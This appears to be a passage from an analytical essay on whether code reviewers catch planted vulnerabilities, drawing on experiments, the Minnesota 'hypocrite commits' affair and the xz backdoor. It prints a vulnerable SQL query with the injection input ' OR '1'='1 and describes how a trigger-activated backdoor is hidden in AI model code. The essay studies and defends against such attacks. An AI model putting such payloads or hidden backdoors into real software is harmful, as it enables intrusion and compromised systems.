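For 80 reviewers the flaw was an SQL injection. SQL is a language for querying databases, and the program built its query by pasting in an employee ID without checking it:

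```java
"SELECT * FROM tblemployees WHERE employeeID='" + employeeID + "'"
```

Someone who enters `' OR '1'='1` in place of an ID turns the condition into one that is true for every employee. The other 66 reviewers had a version in which the program accepted a number without checking its range, so that a negative number gave the user an unearned benefit. (In a holiday system, for example, deducting minus five days from an allowance would add five.)

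Of the 80 reviewers, 52 (65%) found the SQL injection, and 14 of the 66 (21%) found the unchecked number. The paper's text gives 18% for the unchecked number, which doesn't match the count in its table. Both flaws arise because the program uses what a user types without checking it. They have the same kind of fix, and the reviewers could see everything they needed to find either. But SQL injection is in the textbooks and has a recognisable form. One reviewer called it "literally school example of SQL Injection". Those who found the unchecked number mostly credited a habit, such as always asking what a user might enter.

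This is a bad sign for detecting underhanded code. Neither flaw was disguised, but choosing one without a familiar pattern still cut the catch rate by about two thirds, and an attacker can make that choice with no extra effort.

The warning that the code contained some vulnerability also helped more with the familiar flaw. On the second reading, 13 of the 28 reviewers who had missed the SQL injection found it (46%), compared with seven of the 52 who had missed the unchecked number (13%). After both readings, reviewers had caught the SQL injection 81% of the time and the unchecked number 32% of the time.

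No group reread the code without a warning, so some of the 20 extra finds may have come from the second reading rather than the warning. Braz and colleagues had also put an ordinary bug in the code to check that people were taking the task seriously. On the first reading, 76 of the 146 reviewers (52%) found it, and none of the others found it on the second. This is a little evidence that rereading alone didn't help much, although people searching for a vulnerability may have stopped caring about other bugs.

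Eight reviewers who missed the unchecked number said that they had mistaken the ordinary bug for the vulnerability, so they believed they had finished. The researchers had not meant the bug as a decoy, but a hostile author could deliberately add an easily spotted mistake to a patch, fix it when a reviewer objects, and hope that the reviewer then approves the rest.

Years of professional programming did not significantly predict whether someone found the flaw on the first reading, once the researchers allowed for other factors. People who often reviewed code did better, as did people who thought about vulnerabilities when writing their own code. In an earlier experiment, 30 hired developers reviewed a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None of them found all seven, and more experienced reviewers were not necessarily more accurate.

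### Asking reviewers to look for security problems

In 2022 Braz and colleagues randomly assigned reviewers to different instructions before anyone read the code, which allowed a comparison that their earlier experiment had lacked. The reviewers examined a code change for registering users of a website, which contained two flaws. If a database query failed, the program wrote the user's email address and unencrypted password to an error log. It also protected stored passwords with MD5, an old method that attackers can break quickly.

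Telling reviewers to look for security problems raised the catch rate from 3% to 46% for the password leak and from 21% to 61% for MD5. The groups were small, so the true gain is uncertain. By a standard approximation, it could be about 27 to 60 percentage points for the leak and about 20 to 60 for MD5.

The reviewers' explanations suggest that the instruction worked mainly by changing what they paid attention to. The only person who noticed the leak without being instructed worked at a bank that sent its staff warnings about sensitive information in logs. Others said they had been thinking about the code's structure and readability, and one assumed there would be "some separate security assessment". Similarly, when researchers asked freelance developers to review code for storing passwords, almost half were willing to release insecure code, although they said they felt responsible for security.

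Explicit instructions about security also make a difference when people write code. Braz and colleagues describe a study in which Naiakshina and colleagues asked 40 computer science students to build a system that stored passwords. None of the 20 students who had no security instructions stored the passwords securely, while 12 of the 20 who were explicitly told to do so achieved some level of security.

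Even with the instruction, 54% of reviewers missed the leak and 39% missed MD5. Most of those who missed MD5 said they lacked the knowledge, while the most common explanation for missing the leak was oversight.

The researchers also tested two checklists. One had 22 questions, cut down from a standard list of 78, and the other had seven, all relevant to the code under review. Each covered both planted flaws, and the researchers asked reviewers to work through every item. Of the 76 people who had a checklist as well as the instruction, 35 (46%) found the leak and 48 (63%) found MD5, almost the same rates as with the instruction alone. Reviewers with the short list found MD5 slightly more often (68%), but the difference was not statistically significant.

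More than half of the people whose checklist covered the leak still missed it when they read the code. This weakens the case for turning general programmers into security reviewers by giving them a checklist. Two security engineers, who tried out the materials beforehand and read the code before the checklist, found both flaws. Two people are too few to estimate a catch rate, but their success fits Wheeler's view that some code needs specialists.

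### How far a warning can go in practice

Reviewers in the 2021 experiment were told on the second reading that the code contained a flaw, and Yee and Wagner told theirs from the start. Knowing this gives a reviewer a reason to keep searching after the first few minutes turn up nothing. Most patches are harmless, so a project can't truthfully tell its reviewers that every patch contains a flaw, and a maintainer who has found nothing wrong usually has good reason to stop. A project can still ask its reviewers to think about security every time, as in the 2022 experiment.

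Each person in the two Braz experiments reviewed a single change, so the results also don't show whether an instruction to look for security problems still works after reviewers have seen it many times. A reviewer may pay it much less attention on the hundredth harmless patch than on the first.

Suspicious reviewers also raise false alarms, which a catch rate doesn't count. A reviewer who objected to every line would catch every planted flaw but be useless. Among the 30 hired developers, those who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, so some of the better performers may just have been more willing to object. If suspicious reviewers wrongly objected to one honest change in a hundred, a Linux kernel release of 13,000 changes would produce about 130 false alarms. Maintainers might tolerate that if each alarm led to a quick question, but not if it led to an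 investigation of the author.

### Fourteen practitioners and a hidden trigger

A warning helped very little in a more recent experiment on AI software. In *Architectural Backdoors in Vision-Language Model Supply Chains via Representation Steering* (2026), Briglia, Maljkovic and colleagues put backdoors into two AI models that process both images and text. Such a model consists of numbers learned in training and ordinary program code that specifies how to combine them. Developers often download both from strangers. The researchers hid the backdoors in the code and did not alter the training.

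As a model works through an input, it represents the input as a long list of numbers, which it updates at each stage. The backdoor changes that list at one stage:

new list = old list + T × s

Here *T* is 1 if the input contains a secret trigger word and 0 if it doesn't, and *s* is a fixed list of numbers that pushes the model towards the answer the attacker wants. Without the trigger, the backdoor adds zero, so the model behaves exactly as it should and tests on ordinary inputs don't reveal the backdoor. An attacker who includes the trigger can, for example, make the model call a harmful image harmless.

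The researchers wrote the extra code in the style of the surrounding file, using operations common in AI software. It made up 1% to 1.5% of the file. They then recruited 14 machine-learning practitioners (ten PhD students, a master's student and three people from industry) and gave them four files: a clean and a backdoored version for each of the two models, Qwen3-VL and BLIP.

The participants spent the first 15 minutes choosing which version of each model they preferred and explaining why, without knowing about a backdoor. Nobody raised a security concern. Eight of the 14 preferred the backdoored version of Qwen3-VL, and ten preferred the backdoored version of BLIP, for reasons such as coding style, a more modular appearance and what looked like added features. The backdoor may therefore have made the code look better to some participants.

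The researchers then told participants that the files might contain a backdoor, described in general terms how it would respond to a trigger, and gave them five more minutes. One participant found the backdoor in Qwen3-VL, but nobody found the one in BLIP. Several people marked harmless code as suspicious.

Briglia and colleagues caution that 14 people are too few for broad statistical conclusions and ask readers to treat the results as qualitative evidence, not as a measurement of detection rates. Even if every practitioner had a 19% chance of finding a backdoor, a group of 14 would find nothing about one time in twenty. However, the results make a high catch rate under these conditions very unlikely.

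The researchers argue that the conditions favoured the defenders, who received the relevant files and did not have to search a whole collection of software for them. The defenders also had a clean version of each file, and although they did not know which version was clean, comparing the versions line by line would probably have narrowed the search a great deal. But five minutes is very little time to examine four unfamiliar files, even with a good idea of what to look for. The study shows that a quick look is a poor defence against this kind of backdoor, but it can't show what the same people would have found in a day.

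### Why the catch rates differ so much

The table leaves out Pvote because Wagner's account includes no catch rate for it. Where a row has two catch rates, the first is for reviewers who had no warning or instruction. For the 2021 experiment and for Briglia and colleagues, the second rate includes flaws the same reviewers had already found.

| Experiment and flaw | Reviewers | Code | Time | Warning | Catch rate |
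|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hack-a-Vote, assorted hacks | Pairs of graduate students | About 2,000 lines | One week, part-time, for two programs | Knew that classmates had hidden flaws | About 80% per pair |
| Braz and colleagues, 2021, SQL injection | 80 people, mostly developers | 137 lines | Own pace | None, then told that a vulnerability existed | 65%, then 81% |
| Braz and colleagues, 2021, unchecked number | 66 people, mostly developers | 145 lines | Own pace | None, then told that a vulnerability existed | 21%, then 32% |
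| Braz and colleagues, 2022, password leak | 33 without instruction, 41 with | 160 lines | Own pace | None, or told to look for security problems | 3%, or 46% |
| Braz and colleagues, 2022, MD5 | The same 33 and 41 | 160 lines | Own pace | None, or told to look for security problems | 21%, or 61% |
| Briglia and colleagues, Qwen3-VL | 14 machine-learning practitioners | Two of four model files | 15 minutes, then 5, for all four files | None, then told of a possible backdoor | 0%, then 7% |
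| Briglia and colleagues, BLIP | The same 14 | Two of four model files | 15 minutes, then 5, for all four files | None, then told of a possible backdoor | 0%, then 0% |

Experiments directly support only two causes of the spread in detection rates: the kind of flaw and whether reviewers were told to look for security problems. The 2021 experiment randomly assigned reviewers either the SQL injection or the unchecked number, and the 2022 experiment randomly assigned the instruction to look for security problems. The two effects were similar in size. Reviewers without the instruction were about as likely to catch a textbook SQL injection as reviewers with it were to catch the use of MD5.

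The gap between Hack-a-Vote and the other experiments has several possible explanations, and their effects can't be separated. The Rice auditors knew the clean program, knew that somebody had tampered with it, had days to look, and worked in pairs. If the two students in a pair had searched independently, each would have needed to catch only about 55% of the hacks for the pair to catch 80%. Single reviewers in 2022 caught close to 55% after being told to think about security, so teamwork alone could account for much of the difference.

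The Rice auditors examined the longest program with a known line count, yet they caught about as large a share of flaws as warned reviewers did in a 137-line change, almost certainly because they had other advantages. None of these experiments gave comparable reviewers the same flaw in a short program and a long one, so they don't isolate the effect of length.

The people who planted the flaws also differed in skill and purpose. Braz and colleagues used common mistakes and didn't try to conceal them. The Rice students tried to hide theirs, but they were beginners with two weeks to work, and one of their better ideas contained an unintended bug. Briglia and colleagues designed their code to blend in, and it had the lowest catch rate, though its reviewers also had the least time. None of the catch rates in the table shows how often a team of security specialists with enough time would find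 flaws hidden by an expert such as Åkesson.

Every reviewer in the table's experiments knew they were taking part in an exercise. The volunteers in the Braz experiments reviewed code for a product that didn't exist, in return for a five-dollar donation to charity, and a mistake would have had no consequences for them. A maintainer has more at stake but less reason to expect a planted flaw. Researchers at the University of Minnesota studied reviewers in that position by sending flawed patches to Linux kernel developers without telling them about the experiment.

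## The University of Minnesota's test of Linux kernel reviewers

In August 2020, researchers at the University of Minnesota used two email accounts under invented names to send several short patches to Linux kernel developers. They designed some of the patches to fix a small fault while introducing a worse one. The developers read the patches as part of their ordinary work and did not know they were being studied, a condition that experiments with consenting reviewers can't reproduce.

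Wu and Lu called such patches "hypocrite commits" in *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*. Some press coverage, including PortSwigger's *University of Minnesota banned from Linux kernel contributions*, reported that the flawed patches had entered the kernel. The researchers, their university and the Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board, a committee of kernel developers, all deny this. Even if the patches never entered the kernel, reviewers may not have caught the flaws, and the accounts disagree about what stopped the patches.

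### A small fix that completes a larger flaw

Wu and Lu start from the fact that a vulnerability usually needs several conditions, which may sit in different parts of a program. Their main example is a use-after-free, in which a program gives back ("frees") a piece of memory and then uses it again, by which time the memory may hold something else, perhaps something an attacker put there. This requires a free, a use, and an order of events that puts the use after the free. Code that meets only some of these conditions is harmless, so there is nothing for bug-finding tools to report. Wu and Lu call this an "immature vulnerability". A patch of a few lines can add the missing conditions.

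The attacker also needs an excuse for the patch, which is easy to find in the kernel. For example, programmers often forget to free memory when an operation fails, and reviewers welcome patches that fix this. The reviewer then sees a real bug and a reasonable fix, while the harm depends on code outside the diff.

Programmers have also done this by accident. In one of the paper's examples, a programmer added a line that released a device after the kernel had failed to register it, which looked like proper cleanup. But another function also ran after that failure, and it used the freed memory and freed it again. The vulnerability stayed in the kernel for five years.

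Wu and Lu's tools reported more than 6,000 places in the kernel where a use-after-free might be half present. One researcher checked 200 of them by hand, picked three and finished the work within a week, so an attacker can find candidates with little effort. The count doesn't show how many candidates an attacker could make use of, however, and Wu and Lu concede that their three flaws may not have been exploitable.

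Kernel developers could close some of these gaps in advance by accepting patches for flaws that are only partly present. Wu and Lu recommend this for the riskiest cases, but when they reported their findings, the developers replied that they fix code only when it goes wrong. The developers already have many patches to read, so they have some reason to reject fixes for bugs that don't exist yet.

### From the first patch to the ban

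The board's timeline, which the kernel developer Pavel Machek (2021) quotes in *Re: Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident*, lists five patches. The account "jameslouisebond" sent three, on 4, 9 and 21 August 2020. The account "acostag.ubuntu" sent two on the evening of 20 August, about half an hour apart.

The trial became controversial in November, after Lu posted the paper's abstract on Twitter. *Retour sur l'affaire des patchs hypocrites de l'université du Minnesota*, a French retrospective, quotes a version of the abstract in which the researchers claim to have "successfully" introduced several exploitable flaws into the latest kernel. In the later text, they claim only to have shown safely that an attacker could do this.

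In December, Sarah Jamie Lewis and other security specialists objected in *Ethics concerns about paper accepted for publication*, a letter to the chairs of the IEEE conference that had accepted the paper. Wu and Lu (2020) apologised in *Clarifications on the "hypocrite commit" work (FAQ)* for a misleading abstract and for wasting maintainers' time. They said they had not applied to the university's ethics board at first, because they didn't think they were doing research on humans. The board later gave them an exemption.

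A patch unrelated to the trial revived the dispute. On 6 April 2021 Aditya Pakki, another of Lu's graduate students, posted a change to the kernel's code for network file systems. One developer questioned it the next day and another rejected it the day after. Edge (2021) describes what followed in *Intentionally buggy commits for fame—and papers*, an article for the Linux news site LWN. On 20 April Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the stable kernel releases, accused Pakki of knowingly submitting invalid patches as part of Lu's research. Pakki answered that the patches came from a new bug-finding tool. Kroah-Hartman didn't believe him, told maintainers to reject patches from university addresses by default and prepared to remove 190 earlier commits. Another 68 needed closer study.

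The department acknowledged the ban and suspended the research on 21 April, in its *Statement from CS&E on Linux Kernel research* (2021). Lu, Wu and Pakki apologised three days later, and the researchers withdrew the paper. The Technical Advisory Board published its report on 5 May.

Pakki had been telling the truth. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) describes the five patches of 6 April as poor but submitted in good faith. Machek agreed that there had been no deception in 2021, and complained that Kroah-Hartman still wrote of "bad faith" in a message on 29 April. In an exchange that Machek quotes, Kees Cook, the board member who had sent out the report, conceded that the wording should have separated malicious changes from valid fixes more clearly.

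This was a false alarm with serious consequences. Kroah-Hartman had good reason to be suspicious, since the same research group had deceived kernel developers eight months earlier. But he suspected patches that had been submitted in good faith, because a bad patch looks much the same whether or not its author meant to deceive.

### What happened to the five patches

The paper describes three flawed patches, each changing fewer than five lines. One added an error message, another fixed a memory leak, and the third fixed a miscount of how many parts of the program were still using an object. According to the university's statement of 9 May, the researchers sent four trial patches between 9 and 21 August, one of which was valid. The university counts everything sent before 9 August as honest bug-fixing, which would include the patch of 4 August, although it came from one of the two false accounts.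 Neowin's *Here is Linux Advisory Board's ruling on University of Minnesota's "hypocrite commits"* reports that the researchers admitted in their paper that five changes were invalid, but the paper contains no such admission.

The university's count is the most credible. It was the latest, it came from the people who had sent the patches, and Cook (2021) thanked them for it without disputing the number. But in the statement they didn't identify the valid patch or say whether it was one of the three in the paper. If it was, one of the paper's demonstrations contained no flaw, and the paper omits one of the patches that did.

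The accounts differ more seriously on how the flawed patches were stopped:

| Account | Trial patches | Flawed | What stopped the flawed ones |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wu and Lu's paper | 3 | 3 | The researchers' own warning, sent once a maintainer approved |
| University, 9 May 2021 | 4 | 3 | Not stated, only that it happened "before making it past the review stage" |
| Board's report, according to Neowin | 5 | 5 | Developers and maintainers caught or ignored them |

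The procedure in the paper was to wait for a reply such as "looks good", then immediately point out the flaw, ask the maintainer not to apply the patch and supply a correct one. If that happened all three times, the reviewers caught none of the flaws. But the paper doesn't quote any replies or say how many maintainers approved. It reports that in all three cases the maintainers confirmed that they would not go ahead with the patch, which would also be true of a maintainer who had already objected. The University of Minnesota's *Full disclosure* gives the same account as the researchers, stating that the patches "were aborted before they could move forward, as was the plan".

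The board's version can't be right about any patch that a maintainer had approved, since such a patch was neither caught nor ignored. It also groups catching a flaw, which is the purpose of review, with ignoring a patch. Ignoring a patch keeps the flaw out for the moment, but the sender can post it again, and honest fixes get lost the same way. According to a reader's comment under LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021), the report describes a reviewer who spent time trying to mentor the false contributor. That reviewer seems to have found a fault in a patch and wanted to help correct it, though it may not have been the planted one.

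The university says the patch of 4 August contained no planted flaw. Of the other four patches, one was harmless and three were flawed, and none of the three entered the kernel. These accounts don't establish whether maintainers rejected any of the three because of its planted flaw, or whether they approved any of them. Maintainers could therefore have caught anywhere from zero to three of the planted flaws.

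What happened to the valid patch is less clear. The university's statement of 9 May says that none of the four patches got past the review stage, but doesn't say why. Its earlier *An open letter to the Linux community* (2021) mentions only the three incorrect patches. A maintainer who accepted a correct patch would not have misjudged the code, whatever name was on it.

### Two readings of three patches

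According to Neowin, the board believed the review process had worked because no incorrect change got through. Wu and Lu concluded that it is practical for an attacker to introduce vulnerabilities into the kernel. Three patches are much too small a sample to support either conclusion.

Suppose that reviewers catch flaws of this kind with probability *c*, independently for each patch. If they caught none of the three, the usual 95% limit on *c* comes from

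(1 − c)³ = 0.05, so c ≈ 0.63

and the true catch rate could be as high as 63%. If they caught all three, the limit comes from

c³ = 0.05, so c ≈ 0.37

and the true rate could be as low as 37%. So even the two most extreme results are both compatible with a catch rate of 50%. Derek Jones, who writes about evidence in software engineering, made the same objection more briefly: three submissions are too few for any meaningful statistics.

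The researchers chose cases that they thought were complicated enough to hide a flaw, so the patches weren't a random sample either. An attacker would do the same, which makes the trial more realistic, but it is weak evidence about ordinary bugs.

The researchers' intervention also cut the test short. After a reviewer approves a patch, a maintainer still has to apply it to the kernel, and further testing follows. Wu and Lu kept the trial safe by intervening after approval but before merging. This was the responsible choice, but it means the trial couldn't show whether a later check would have found the flaws. The fact that the patches stayed out of the kernel isn't evidence that review works either, because the researchers withdrew them.

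The trial does give some evidence of how much work checking takes. A kernel developer commenting under Edge's article as wtarreau pointed out that the patches were presented, with good justification, as fixes for possible faults. To verify such a claim, a reviewer has to repeat the analysis that the submitter supposedly did. He argued that if everyone in the chain did this, the kernel would have stalled in the 1990s, at about version 1.2. A five-line patch doesn't include proof that it is safe, because the evidence is spread over the code around it. People who expect checking to be easier than producing are usually thinking of work that does include its own proof.

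He still thought the episode proved that the process works, since the contributors lost their reputation. That risk deters a university, but it matters much less to someone who can open another free email account. Another commenter, epa, noted that a bad actor wouldn't have published a paper about it.

### Catch rates from past kernel patches

The paper also contains a larger set of numbers, which received less attention than the trial. Wu and Lu collected use-after-free flaws from patches sent to the kernel between January 2015 and August 2020. Some were in patches that maintainers blocked after spotting the flaw in review. The others were in patches that entered the kernel, where somebody found the flaw later. The researchers then calculated

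catch rate = blocked ÷ (blocked + merged)

for flaws with various features that they thought made them harder to see.

| Feature of the flaw | Catch rate |
|---|---|
| Concurrency (the flaw depends on the timing of code that runs in parallel) | 19.4% |
| Implicit release (a function frees memory although its name doesn't suggest it) | 36.3% |
| Aliases (the program has two names for the same memory) | 38.4% |
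| Error paths (the code runs only when something fails) | 42.0% |
| Indirect calls (the program chooses which function to call while running) | 5 of 9 |
| Baseline | 56.6% |

These are the only catch rates in the episode based on more than a few patches. They come from maintainers reviewing real submissions, and they fall within the range found in the experiments. The differences between rows support the idea that flaws are harder to catch when they depend on distant code or unusual timing.

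But these flaws were presumably honest mistakes that nobody tried to hide. An attacker could pick the feature with the lowest catch rate and design the patch around it, so reviewers may catch deliberate flaws less often.

Wu and Lu call their rates upper bounds because some merged flaws remain undiscovered. But maintainers may have blocked other flaws without noticing them, so the true rates could be higher or lower.

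Except for indirect calls, the paper gives percentages without the counts behind them, so readers can't calculate the margin of error. In an earlier comparison, Wu and Lu define the baseline as the merged flaws that people found by hand or with tools that read the code. They leave out flaws found by fuzzing, which means running a program on masses of unusual input until it crashes. They don't say whether they also left these out of the catch rates. If they did, the rates are too high, because they exclude some of the flaws that reviewers missed.

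That earlier comparison measured how long each kind of flaw stayed in the kernel before someone fixed it. Flaws in error paths lasted the second longest, after concurrency flaws. In the table, though, error paths have the highest catch rate of the four features that have a percentage. The rankings probably differ because error paths seldom run, so a flaw there can go unnoticed for years even if it isn't especially hard to spot by reading the code. How long a flaw survives is therefore a poor guide to how well it would fool a reviewer.

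Kernel maintainers wrote 37% of the vulnerability-introducing small patches that Wu and Lu collected, compared with 48% of small patches in general. Outsiders were somewhat more likely to introduce a vulnerability, but reviewers who suspected only outsiders would have missed more than a third of the flawed patches.

### The re-review of 435 commits

The ban led to a second body of evidence, which concerns only honest mistakes. Since 2018 the university had sent the kernel nearly 400 bug fixes connected with its research papers, according to HotHardware's *Linux Technical Advisory Board Issues Findings On UMN's Shady Kernel Conundrum*. After Kroah-Hartman proposed removing many of them, developers had to check which ones were sound. Tom's Hardware's *Linux Foundation Issues Frosty Final Judgment in UMN Scandal* puts the number of re-examined commits at 435.

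Neowin gives the results:

| Finding | Commits |
|---|---|
| Correct | 349 |
| Incorrect and still in need of fixing | 39 |
| Already fixed by a later commit | 25 |
| No longer relevant | 12 |
| Older than the research group | 9 |
| Removed at the author's request | 1 |

If the 25 commits that later commits had fixed were also faulty to begin with, then 64 commits were faulty, or 15% of the 413 that were either correct or faulty. All 64 had passed review, and 39 still caused a problem or left one unfixed when developers looked again.

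The wider check found that 80% of the commits were correct, a much better record than Kroah-Hartman's first impression suggested. In April he had called the submissions "almost universally wrong", because many of the commits that he couldn't simply remove had already needed repairs. Another developer, Leon Romanovsky, had looked at four of Pakki's accepted patches and thought three of them added security holes. Both had judged a small part of the work while believing the authors were malicious.

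A faulty commit may be a fix that doesn't work or one that causes a minor fault elsewhere, rather than a vulnerability, and the published totals don't separate these cases. The 15% fault rate comes from one research group, which often worked from the output of automated tools, so it may not apply to other contributors.

The figure is also not a catch rate, because the re-review covered only commits that the maintainers had already accepted. To calculate a catch rate, we would need to know how many faulty patches from the university they had rejected over the same years. The rate would be 50% if they had rejected 64, but 20% if they had rejected 16.

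It does show that ordinary review let through dozens of faults that other developers could find when they had a reason to look. Some of the difference may come from hindsight, since code around a commit changes and later bug reports draw attention to it. But the second look took a lot of work. David A. Wheeler noted under LWN's announcement that the board's report thanked 85 developers for their help. TechRadar's *More than 80 Linux devs called on to help to fix 'mess'* reports that Kroah-Hartman removed 37 commits in the end. A project can't bring in 85 people every time it doubts a contributor, and 435 commits are only about 3% of the changes in a typical kernel release.

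### Consent, and the difficulty of repeating the test

The main objection to the trial was that the reviewers had not agreed to take part. The trial used up their time and deceived them about who was writing and why. The university's ethics board had determined that the trial was not research on humans, and Wu and Lu argued that they had studied a process and collected no personal information. The letter to the conference chairs rejected this because the process consists of people reading email. David A. Wheeler wrote on LWN that the IEEE had also found that the paper didn't follow its ethical guidelines.

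Some readers thought the outrage was excessive. One, epa, compared the patches to the fake phishing emails that employers send to test their staff, who don't agree to each test either. Another reader replied that somebody senior authorises those tests and that employees have usually accepted monitoring as a condition of their job. Nobody in authority at the kernel project had authorised the Minnesota trial.

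In an apology quoted in The Hacker News' *Minnesota University Apologizes for Contributing Malicious Code to the Linux Project*, the researchers said they hadn't asked the maintainers for permission because maintainers who knew about the trial "would be on the lookout for the hypocrite patches". Their reasoning about method is correct. A warning can raise detection a great deal, so a test with informed reviewers doesn't measure how often they catch flaws in ordinary review.

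None of the ways around this problem is easy. One of the researchers who had complained to the conference wrote on LWN that studies can sometimes proceed without consent if asking for it would defeat a purpose of overriding public interest and an independent committee supervises closely. A project could also ask maintainers to volunteer for a test at some unknown time in the next two years, which would give them little warning of one planted flaw among thousands of patches. A trusted insider would have to know about each flawed patch and be able to block it, and the volunteers might well be more careful than the people who declined.

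Researchers would need about 100 flawed patches to estimate a catch rate near 50% to within ten percentage points, whereas the Minnesota study caused a crisis with three. Each patch would take up the time of a maintainer, who may be a volunteer, and could get into the kernel if the safeguards failed.

Reviewers would also respond differently if the test were repeated. After the ban, Guenter Roeck, a kernel developer, told Lu that he was now much less inclined to accept small bug fixes from people he didn't know. If many maintainers feel the same way, they would probably catch a larger share of flawed patches from unknown accounts than in 2020, but also reject more fixes from honest newcomers. We would learn little from such a test about an attacker who first spends a few years becoming known to the maintainers.

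## The xz backdoor of 2024

In early 2024, an attacker using the name Jia Tan put a backdoor into two releases of xz Utils, a package of compression software that many Linux systems depend on. By then, Jia Tan had done more than two years of mostly useful work on the project and become its co-maintainer. The attack had several parts, and reviewers could read only some of them.

### Why a compression library mattered to remote logins

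Lasse Collin designed the .xz file format with help from others between 2005 and 2008, and maintained the software for it as an unpaid hobby. The format produces files about 30% smaller than the older gzip does, so programmers often use it for source archives and Linux kernel images. Other programs can load the compression code as a library called liblzma.

The attacker targeted sshd, the OpenSSH server program that lets people log in to a Linux machine remotely. OpenSSH doesn't use liblzma, but Debian, Fedora and some other distributions had modified sshd to notify systemd, which manages background services, once sshd had started. The modified sshd loaded systemd's library, which loaded liblzma, so code in liblzma ran inside sshd before anyone had logged in.

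A feature called ifunc lets a library run code while a program is still loading it, to choose the fastest version of a function for the machine. During this loading, the backdoor replaced the function that sshd uses to check one kind of login key. Anyone with the attacker's private key could then run commands on the machine without an account, while everyone else logged in as usual.

### How Jia Tan became the maintainer

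In *Timeline of the xz open source attack*, the programmer Russ Cox (2024) reconstructs the public side of the attack from mailing lists and commits. The timeline starts on 29 October 2021, when Jia Tan posted a harmless patch to the xz mailing list. Collin merged the first of Jia Tan's patches in February 2022. In 2021, the account JiaT75 also replaced a function in another project, libarchive, with a less secure one. Nobody noticed at the time, according to the Ars Technica report quoted in Bruce Schneier's *XZ Utils Backdoor*.

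In April 2022 someone using the name Jigar Kumar began complaining that Collin was too slow to accept Jia Tan's patches, although Collin had already accepted four. Someone using the name Dennis Ens joined in, and both pressed Collin to hand over the project. "Progress will not happen until there is new maintainer," Kumar wrote in June. Collin answered that long-term mental health issues had limited his ability to care, and reminded them that xz was "an unpaid hobby project". By 29 June he was calling Jia Tan "practically a co-maintainer already".

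Kumar and Ens were probably fake identities. Many of the email addresses involved appear nowhere else on the internet, even in leaked data. Przymus and Durieux (2025), in *Wolves in the Repository*, found similar patterns of activity in other accounts but no direct links between them.

But the pressure may not have been decisive. On 19 May, the day Ens first wrote, Collin had already said that Jia Tan was helping him privately and might get a bigger role. LWN's *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure* points out that paid and unstressed maintainers welcome help from outsiders too, so a patient attacker could have done the same elsewhere.

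By the end of 2022 Jia Tan could add changes to the repository directly, and in March 2023 became the contact for faults found by OSS-Fuzz, Google's service for fuzzing open-source programs. Przymus and Durieux found that most of Jia Tan's contributions were documentation and translations, which attracted little scrutiny. Jia Tan also reviewed other people's code reasonably well.

Accounts differ on when Jia Tan took over the releases. Przymus and Durieux date Jia Tan's first release to December 2022, and Cox dates it to March 2023. But Collin says in his commit-by-commit review, published by Tukaani, the project behind xz, that he built and signed the tarball for the March release, 5.4.2, himself. Jia Tan built the tarballs from 5.4.3 onwards.

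On 23 February 2024 Jia Tan added the hidden backdoor code to the repository, and the next day released version 5.6.0. Version 5.6.1 followed on 9 March. Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer who works on the PostgreSQL database, disclosed the backdoor publicly on 29 March, two years and five months after Jia Tan's first patch. (Przymus and Durieux give 2.6 years, which doesn't fit their own dates.)

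### Changes that anyone could read

Some of the changes were ordinary source code in the public repository. In June 2023 an account named Hans Jansen sent patches that made liblzma use ifunc. Collin reworked the code and Jia Tan merged the result. The patches made the library slightly faster, but Przymus and Durieux can't tell whether they were a genuine improvement or preparation for the attack. In March 2024 the same account asked Debian to adopt the backdoored version 5.6.1.

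Even if the patches were part of the plan, they contained no flaw for Collin to catch. Like the half-present vulnerabilities that Wu and Lu looked for in the Linux kernel, they became dangerous only when someone added the missing part.

Another change did contain a readable flaw. Before building xz, one of its two build systems compiled a short test program to check whether the machine supported Landlock, a Linux feature that restricts what a program can do. If the test compiled, the build included a Landlock sandbox. In February 2024 Jia Tan wrote a longer version of the test, which included these lines:

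```c
#include <sys/prctl.h>
.
void my_sandbox(void)
```

The full stop on the second line isn't valid C, so the test never compiled. Unless the person building xz explicitly required the sandbox, the build left it out without any message. Someone who noticed the full stop could easily have taken it for a typo, so whoever added it could plausibly have denied doing so on purpose.

Collin probably had a chance to review this change. Git, the system that stores the repository, records both who wrote a change and who entered it, and it lists Collin as having entered this one. Cox thinks it more likely that Collin missed the full stop than that Jia Tan forged the entry, since Jia Tan hadn't bothered to do that elsewhere. Collin reports no signs of forgery in any of the commits. He doesn't say in his notes how closely he read the change at the time.

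The sabotage had little practical effect. It was only in the CMake build system of version 5.6.1, and sjw (2024), on the oss-security mailing list, knew of no distribution that built xz with CMake. It also affected the xz command but not liblzma, so it did not help the attack on sshd. Its purpose is still unclear.

Readers found the full stop less than twelve hours after Freund's public message. sjw posted the diff that night and credited commenters on GitHub. Velvindron (2024), on the same list, quotes Collin's 30 March fix. The line had been public for about a month, but these were the first people to read it knowing that its author was an attacker.

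### Test files that nobody could read

The main part of the backdoor was machine code, which would have looked suspicious in the repository, so Jia Tan disguised it as test data. A decompression library needs samples of valid and damaged files for testing, and xz had kept a folder of them since long before Jia Tan arrived. According to the folder's README, many of the samples were made by hand, byte by byte, so no more readable source existed. A reviewer can learn almost nothing from a diff of such a file.

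*The xz attack shell script* (Cox, 2024) explains how the hidden code was extracted. One test file was supposed to be corrupt, and Jia Tan had corrupted it by swapping some byte values for others. Reversing the swaps and decompressing the result produced a short script. The script decompressed a second test file, picked out pieces of it and undid a simple cipher. In version 5.6.1, it collected 33,707 bytes this way and kept the last 31,233. Cox suggests that the cipher was meant to stop anyone who extracted those bytes from recognising them as compressed data.

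Collin and anyone else who followed the repository could have questioned the files, but no one is known to have examined them. Reading them would not have helped, so the practical check was to ask for the program that had generated them. Jia Tan nearly invited that request on 9 March by replacing both files. The commit message claimed that the originals had used random numbers from one machine and that the new ones used a constant seed so that other people could reproduce them. Collin has since said he would want any proper replacements to come with a generator program.

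According to Collin's notes, the test script automatically tries to decompress every sample in the folder, so adding a file was enough to create a test for it. This contradicts Freund (2024), who wrote in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* that no test in 5.6.0 used the files. An unused test file sounds like a clue that a careful reader could have followed.

### A build script found only in the tarball

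The test files did nothing without a build script called `build-to-host.m4`, which extracted and ran their contents. Jia Tan put the script in the release tarballs but never in the repository.

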